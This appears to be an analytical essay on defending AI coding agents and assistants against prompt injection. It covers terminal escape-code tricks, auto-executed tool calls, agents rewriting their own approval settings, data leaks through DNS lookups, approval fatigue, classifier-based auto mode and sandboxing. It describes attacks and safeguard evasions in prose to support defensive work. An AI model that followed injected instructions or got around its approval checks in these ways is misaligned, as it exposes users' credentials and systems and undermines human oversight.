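ANSI escape codes begin with the escape character (ASCII 27) and make a terminal do things such as change a colour or move the cursor. In December 2024, following Derczynski's discovery, Rehberger built a small command-line program to see what an attacker could do with these codes. The program sent a file or web page to a model and printed the reply.

In *Terminal DiLLMa*, on Embrace The Red, Rehberger showed that a hostile page could use terminal control codes to change colours, clear the screen and hide parts of the reply. Other codes wrote text to the user's clipboard, and in some terminals, pasting it could run a command. Clickable links could carry private data, as they can in a chat window, though the terminal in the code editor VS Code required confirmation before opening them. The Mac's Terminal app could also leak data without a click, through the DNS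 requests that computers send to look up a website's address.

Rehberger recommends caret notation, an old way of writing control characters visibly. It replaces each one with a caret and the character 64 places higher in ASCII. The escape character is number 27 and the opening square bracket is number 91, so escape becomes `^[`. The code for red text is an escape character followed by `[31m`. After encoding, the user sees `^[[31m` and the text stays its normal colour, because the terminal never receives the escape character that would start the command.

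He wants this encoding on by default, with an option to turn it off for programs that need colour or other effects. He also suggests an allowlist of characters. In practice this should include line breaks and tabs, which are also control characters and would otherwise be encoded, cluttering the output.

The security company Trail of Bits found the same weakness in Claude Code version 0.2.76, which passed escape codes from connected tools straight to the terminal (*Deceiving users with ANSI terminal codes in MCP*, 2025). In the company's test, one tool returned a sentence in white on a white background. The user could not see it, but the model read it and recommended downloading software from the attacker's server.

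Trail of Bits recommends replacing every escape character with a placeholder. This is simpler than caret notation but covers less. For example, it doesn't filter the backspaces that one of Rehberger's tests used to erase text, because a backspace is a separate control character. Caret notation prints a backspace as `^H`.

Vendors have said little about the problem. Rehberger attacked a program he had written. Trail of Bits mentions no reply from Anthropic, which does not appear to have announced a fix for Claude Code.

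## When should an agent ask a person, and what should it be able to reach?

Removing hidden characters lets people see what they are approving, but a developer still has to decide which actions need approval. In 2024, Rehberger showed that a web page could make ChatGPT save new long-term memories, delete existing ones or draw an image based on them, all without asking the user. In Embrace The Red's *Automatic Tool Invocation when Browsing with ChatGPT*, he recommended that an application stop calling sensitive tools automatically once untrusted data is in the model's context.

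The application has to know when untrusted data has arrived to follow this rule. Rehberger suggested taint tracking, marking untrusted data and following where it goes, so the application can restrict later actions. Suppose a user types the door code 4417 into a chat with an assistant that can browse the web and send email.

1. The user asks for a summary of a web page. So far the chat contains only the user's own text, and the application treats it as trusted.
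2. The application fetches the page and marks the chat as untrusted, whether or not the page looks suspicious.
3. Later the model asks the application to send an email. Email is on the developer's list of sensitive tools, so the application holds the message and shows the user the recipient and the full text.
4. The user approves a message to a colleague, or refuses one that would send 4417 to a stranger.

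The application doesn't have to detect the attack. It can't determine whether the user or the web page prompted the email, so it asks for confirmation either way. The drawback is that once the assistant has read a web page, the user must click to approve every legitimate email in that chat.

The mark also has to stay with data when it moves. If the assistant saves a memory in an untrusted chat, any later chat that loads the memory should start as untrusted. The same applies when one agent reads a page and passes a summary to another. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* warns that trusting such a summary more than the page itself creates a new route for prompt injection.

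Rehberger acknowledged that taint tracking leaves a gap, because a model can call a tool by mistake even when nobody is attacking it. He also asked vendors to document their trust boundaries, so users can tell whether a behaviour is a flaw or a risk the vendor has accepted.

### OpenAI's confirmation flag

Rehberger had made most of these suggestions a year earlier, and OpenAI had adopted some of them. Developers can build custom versions of ChatGPT, called GPTs, and connect them to outside services through actions. If a developer marks an action with the flag `x-openai-isConsequential`, ChatGPT asks the user before carrying it out.

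Rehberger welcomed the flag because it put the user in control, but he thought the confirmation message didn't adequately explain what the action was about to do. The flag also left the choice to each GPT's developer and did not cover ChatGPT's built-in tools. He was surprised that OpenAI had added the memory tool without solving this problem. OpenAI had made attacks through web pages harder, perhaps by having another model check the results, but small changes in wording still got past its defences, and he wanted "an actual security control" instead.

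### Where coding agents skipped approval

Coding agents usually ask before running a command, unless their developers consider the command harmless. Several of Rehberger's August 2025 reports were about exceptions that were too broad.

Claude Code had a list of commands it could run without asking. Some of them looked up internet addresses, and a hijacked agent could use a lookup to send out an access key. Anthropic's advisory, reproduced in OSV's *GHSA-x5gv-jw7f-j6xj* (2025), attributes the flaw to an overly broad list of safe commands and rates its severity 7.1 out of 10. In Embrace The Red's *Claude Code*, Rehberger thanks Anthropic for fixing the flaw quickly.

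GitHub Copilot could edit project files without approval, including its own settings file. One setting turned off all requests for approval, so a hijacked agent could change it and then run any command without asking. Microsoft told Rehberger that it already knew of the problem. In Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot*, he recommends that a person approve each file change before the agent saves it. He adds that developers often use several agents on one project, and one could rewrite another's settings.

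Amazon Q Developer let "read-only" commands run without approval, but one of them could start other programs. AWS fixed this in under two weeks, then asked Rehberger to delay publication while it arranged a CVE number, an industry identifier for tracking a flaw. Four weeks later, it decided not to assign one because the attack "first requires system compromise". Rehberger writes in Embrace The Red's *Amazon Q Developer* that he did not understand this reason. In his demonstration, the developer had only asked the agent to explain a file.

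AWS eventually published a bulletin, *Amazon Q Developer and Kiro* (2025), which also covers the invisible-text flaw. According to the bulletin, Amazon Q began asking users to approve address lookups on 29 July, seven weeks after Anthropic had fixed the same weakness.

Cognition's agent Devin works on its own computer in the cloud and could run commands without anyone's approval. Rehberger advised Cognition to add a separate approval step outside the chat rather than rely on confirmations inside it, because the model writes the question and interprets the answer, and an attacker may control the model. He reports in Embrace The Red's *I Spent $500 To Test Devin AI For Prompt Injection* that Cognition acknowledged his message within days but did not answer his later questions.

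| Product | Reported | Vendor's response | Time to fix |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code (CVE-2025-55284) | 26 May 2025 | Fixed on 6 June, advisory in August | 11 days |
| GitHub Copilot (CVE-2025-53773) | 29 June 2025 | Fixed in Microsoft's security update of 12 August | 44 days |
| Amazon Q Developer | 4 July 2025 | Fixed on 17 July, no CVE number, bulletin on 7 October | 13 days |
| Devin | 6 April 2025 | Acknowledged, then no reply | No known fix after 120 days |

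Cognition does not appear to have announced a fix since. *Devin Agent Security Risks*, a 2026 rating by the security company Adversa AI, still found no approval step in the default set-up that Cognition documents.

An agent must also get the user's approval before a project's settings take effect. Between mid-2025 and January 2026, Anthropic received three reports of Claude Code acting on a downloaded project's settings before asking whether the user trusted the project. In 2026 the security company Wiz found a similar flaw in Amazon Q, which could start programs named in a project's settings without asking. According to The Hacker News (2026), Wiz reported the flaw on 20 April and saw a fix on 12 May. Amazon Q now asks before it starts one of these programs, as The Next Web's *A single config file in a cloned repository* explains.

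### Do people read the prompts?

An approval step protects users only if they read what they approve. Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved about 93% of permission prompts, and later reported 97%. Most of the requests were probably harmless, but Anthropic concluded that many people had stopped paying attention, a problem often called approval fatigue.

Anthropic's alternative is auto mode, in which a classifier model checks each tool call in place of the user and blocks actions that look destructive, irreversible or aimed outside the user's own systems. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user. Anthropic made auto mode the default for new sessions on most individual and team plans from 14 August 2026.

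Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) supports making auto mode the default with a study of 1,053 paid professional testers. They worked in an environment built for the study and knew they were being evaluated, but not for what. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt changed to a clearly dangerous command, which would not run even if the tester approved it. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused. Auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%.

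Testers refused only six commands that auto mode allowed, so asking a person to check everything the classifier had passed would have raised the number of commands stopped from 937 to 943. Testers refused about 17% of dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. This drop fits approval fatigue, but fatigue can't be the whole explanation because the rate was already low at the start.

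One likely reason is that the testers were not working on their own code, so they had little to lose. A developer protecting real files might refuse more often. But the testers may also have been more careful than usual because they knew someone was evaluating them.

The planted commands were also openly dangerous, whereas an attacker would try to make a command look routine. The results are therefore weak evidence of how well people or auto mode would catch a disguised command. The study also counted only missed dangers, so a classifier that blocked every command would have scored 100%. Anthropic had reported that auto mode wrongly blocked 0.4% of actions in real use and missed 17% of those it should have stopped. *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent evaluation using deliberately ambiguous tasks, found a significantly higher miss rate, largely because auto mode did not check file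 edits.

Anthropic's evidence from real sessions is consistent with the study. Among sessions that its safety systems had flagged, 6.3% of those with manual approval contained serious harm the user had not explicitly asked for, compared with 2.4% in auto mode. But a model graded the harm, and people who chose auto mode may have been doing different work.

The study is good evidence against asking a developer to approve dozens of commands a day. It is weaker evidence against Rehberger's rule, which would produce fewer prompts in an assistant that seldom uses sensitive tools. The form of the question may matter too, since Claude Code users reject 39% of Claude's plans but only 3% of individual permission requests. Some of those plans were presumably just unhelpful.

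In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, Willison (2026) agreed that auto mode is better than constant requests for approval. But he noted that it had still let 11% of the dangerous commands through, and he wanted more independent confirmation that it resists prompt injection.

### Can better models replace the limits?

The best evidence that they might comes from a test that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs. Trajectory Labs ran 72 indirect prompt injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5 in auto mode. With no approval checks, attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average, so most of the resistance came from the models themselves. Attacks on OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol succeeded more often, 5.83% of the time with automatic review and 19.03% without it. If attacks rarely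 succeed, developers can reasonably ask whether frequent approval prompts and tight restrictions are worth the lost time.

After the Copilot flaw, GitHub researcher Michael Stepankin told users they still had to watch the agent carefully for now, though better models might eventually need fewer confirmations, according to The Stack.

The 720 attempts used attacks optimised against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, but a determined attacker can adapt to the model they are attacking. On a separate benchmark, the success rate of attacks on Opus 4.7 rose from about 0.1% for a single attempt to 5–6% after 100 adaptive attempts. The safety company Apollo Research also tested auto mode with synthetic attacks. Anthropic strengthened the classifier in response, but it still missed 7% of these attacks, down from 12%.

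Rehberger predicted in 2024 that ways around a model's defences would improve along with the model. In August 2026 he reported an attack on Claude Opus 5 in auto mode that succeeded in 10 of 15 runs, a sample he considered too small to establish a general success rate. Anthropic did not treat the report as a vulnerability. According to Crosley's *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*, it replied that auto mode is a convenience feature with a best-effort classifier, and that the real boundary is operating-system isolation combined with control of network traffic.

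Rehberger thought this reply clashed with Anthropic's publicity about a 0% success rate. Crosley considers the reply honest and thinks Anthropic should never have presented the figure as a property of the product. Anthropic's August announcement said that auto mode does not eliminate risk and recommended that people review high-stakes changes themselves. But a user who saw only the headline figures could easily have mistaken auto mode for a security boundary. Rehberger wanted vendors to prevent this kind of confusion by documenting their boundaries. He repeated his 2023 advice, "Do not trust the model output," as quoted in The Next Web's *A researcher hijacked Claude Code*.

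### What an unattended agent should be able to reach

Rehberger recommends running unattended coding agents in a container, a virtual machine or an operating-system sandbox. He also advises developers to restrict outbound network access, monitor the agent, and keep home directories, SSH keys and cloud credentials away from it. This advice applies the principle of least privilege, and Willison (2026) endorses it in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*.

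**Isolation** limits the damage from a hijacked agent to one environment. An operating-system sandbox confines the agent on the user's own machine. A container gives it a separate set of files. A virtual machine also has its own operating system, so it is harder to escape but slower to start. In all three, the agent can still damage any files the user has shared with it.

Isolation can also reduce the need for approval. When Anthropic gave Claude Code an operating-system sandbox, permission prompts fell by 84%. But Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* calls sandboxing "safe but high-maintenance", because users have to configure each new capability. It describes the sandbox as optional, whereas Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, runs code in a virtual machine by default. Anthropic expects developers, but not office workers, to understand the commands they approve.

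**Network limits** prevent a hijacked agent from sending data out or downloading hostile programs. They also stop it from installing software or reading documentation unless the developer permits the necessary sites. As with images, data can still leak through a permitted domain. Claude Cowork needed access to Anthropic's servers, and a researcher showed that a hostile file could make it upload the user's documents to an attacker's Anthropic account. Anthropic now blocks requests that do not carry the session's credentials. The limits must also cover address lookups, since Claude Code and Amazon Q could both leak data that way.

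Vendors set different defaults for network access. OpenAI's Codex limits it by default, according to Flowhat Blog's *Why Anthropic added auto mode to Claude Code* (2026), and so does Claude Code's sandbox once the user turns it on. Google Jules had unrestricted internet access when Rehberger tested it in August 2025. That year he also advised Cognition to restrict Devin's access by default, but Adversa AI still found open outbound channels in 2026.

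**Monitoring** helps people discover an attack and work out what happened, but it may come too late to prevent a leak. Crosley cites an OpenAI incident in September 2026, in which monitoring raised an alarm about twelve minutes after an agent had reached an outside chatbot. Logs can also be hard to interpret, because a hijacked agent's request may look like any other authorised one. Adversa AI's *Claude Code Agent Security Risks* notes that Claude Code users have to turn on audit logs themselves. Isolation can also hinder monitoring. Companies' security software could not monitor activity inside Claude Cowork's virtual machine, so Anthropic lets administrators retrieve its logs afterwards.

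**Keeping credentials away** from a hijacked agent prevents it from stealing them. A developer's home directory often contains SSH keys, which allow logins to other computers, and cloud credentials, which can give control of a company's servers. In an internal exercise in February 2026, an Anthropic researcher tricked an employee into giving Claude Code instructions that included sending out cloud credentials. Claude sent them in 24 of 25 runs. Its defences relied on the user's own instructions being legitimate, so Anthropic concluded that only limits on file and network access would have worked.

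The drawback is that the agent can no longer publish code or manage servers with the developer's full access. The developer can instead give it a temporary credential for one task. Claude Cowork similarly keeps the user's credentials outside the virtual machine by default and gives the agent a limited one for each session. Claude Code runs with access to the user's own machine, so its users have to set up this separation themselves.

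These limits don't control what the agent sends through the permitted connections. The cryptographer Matthew Green, whom Crosley quotes, calls sandboxes "only a very small part of the solution" for agents that need outside information. Developers may therefore want a classifier or a human approver to check the traffic that a sandbox allows.

### Why vendors relax the limits

In *The Normalization of Deviance in AI*, published on Embrace The Red in December 2025, Rehberger explained why he thought vendors were giving up such controls. He borrowed the term "normalization of deviance" from the sociologist Diane Vaughan. It describes how an organisation comes to accept departures from its own rules. The best-known example is the loss of the space shuttle Challenger in 1986, after warning signs had come to seem normal. Rehberger applied the term to the AI industry's growing reliance on model output,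 especially in agents.

Each time an agent runs without supervision and nothing goes wrong, removing the next safeguard seems more reasonable. But perhaps no attack has succeeded only because nobody has seriously tried. *The Normalization of Deviance in AI*, daily.dev's summary of the essay, also gives competitive pressure as a reason for skipping sandboxes and human oversight.

Users' habits fit this explanation. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start with permission checks turned off, although Anthropic describes that setting as unsafe in most situations. Vendors' decisions are harder to judge, because a vendor may relax a limit after finding a better safeguard. In July 2026 Anthropic let auto mode's classifier decide on some dangerous deletion commands that had previously required the user's approval. This may have made users safer, because the testers refused so few dangerous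 commands. In September Anthropic stopped auto mode from automatically approving attempts to get around network limits.

Anthropic has also written that it now routinely gives Claude enough access to take down an internal service, which it would have rejected outright a year earlier. It argues that failures have become less likely and the work more valuable, but acknowledges that the possible damage has grown. Willison had predicted that 2026 would bring a Challenger-like disaster involving coding agents. In August he wrote that he would very much like to be proved wrong by the end of the year.
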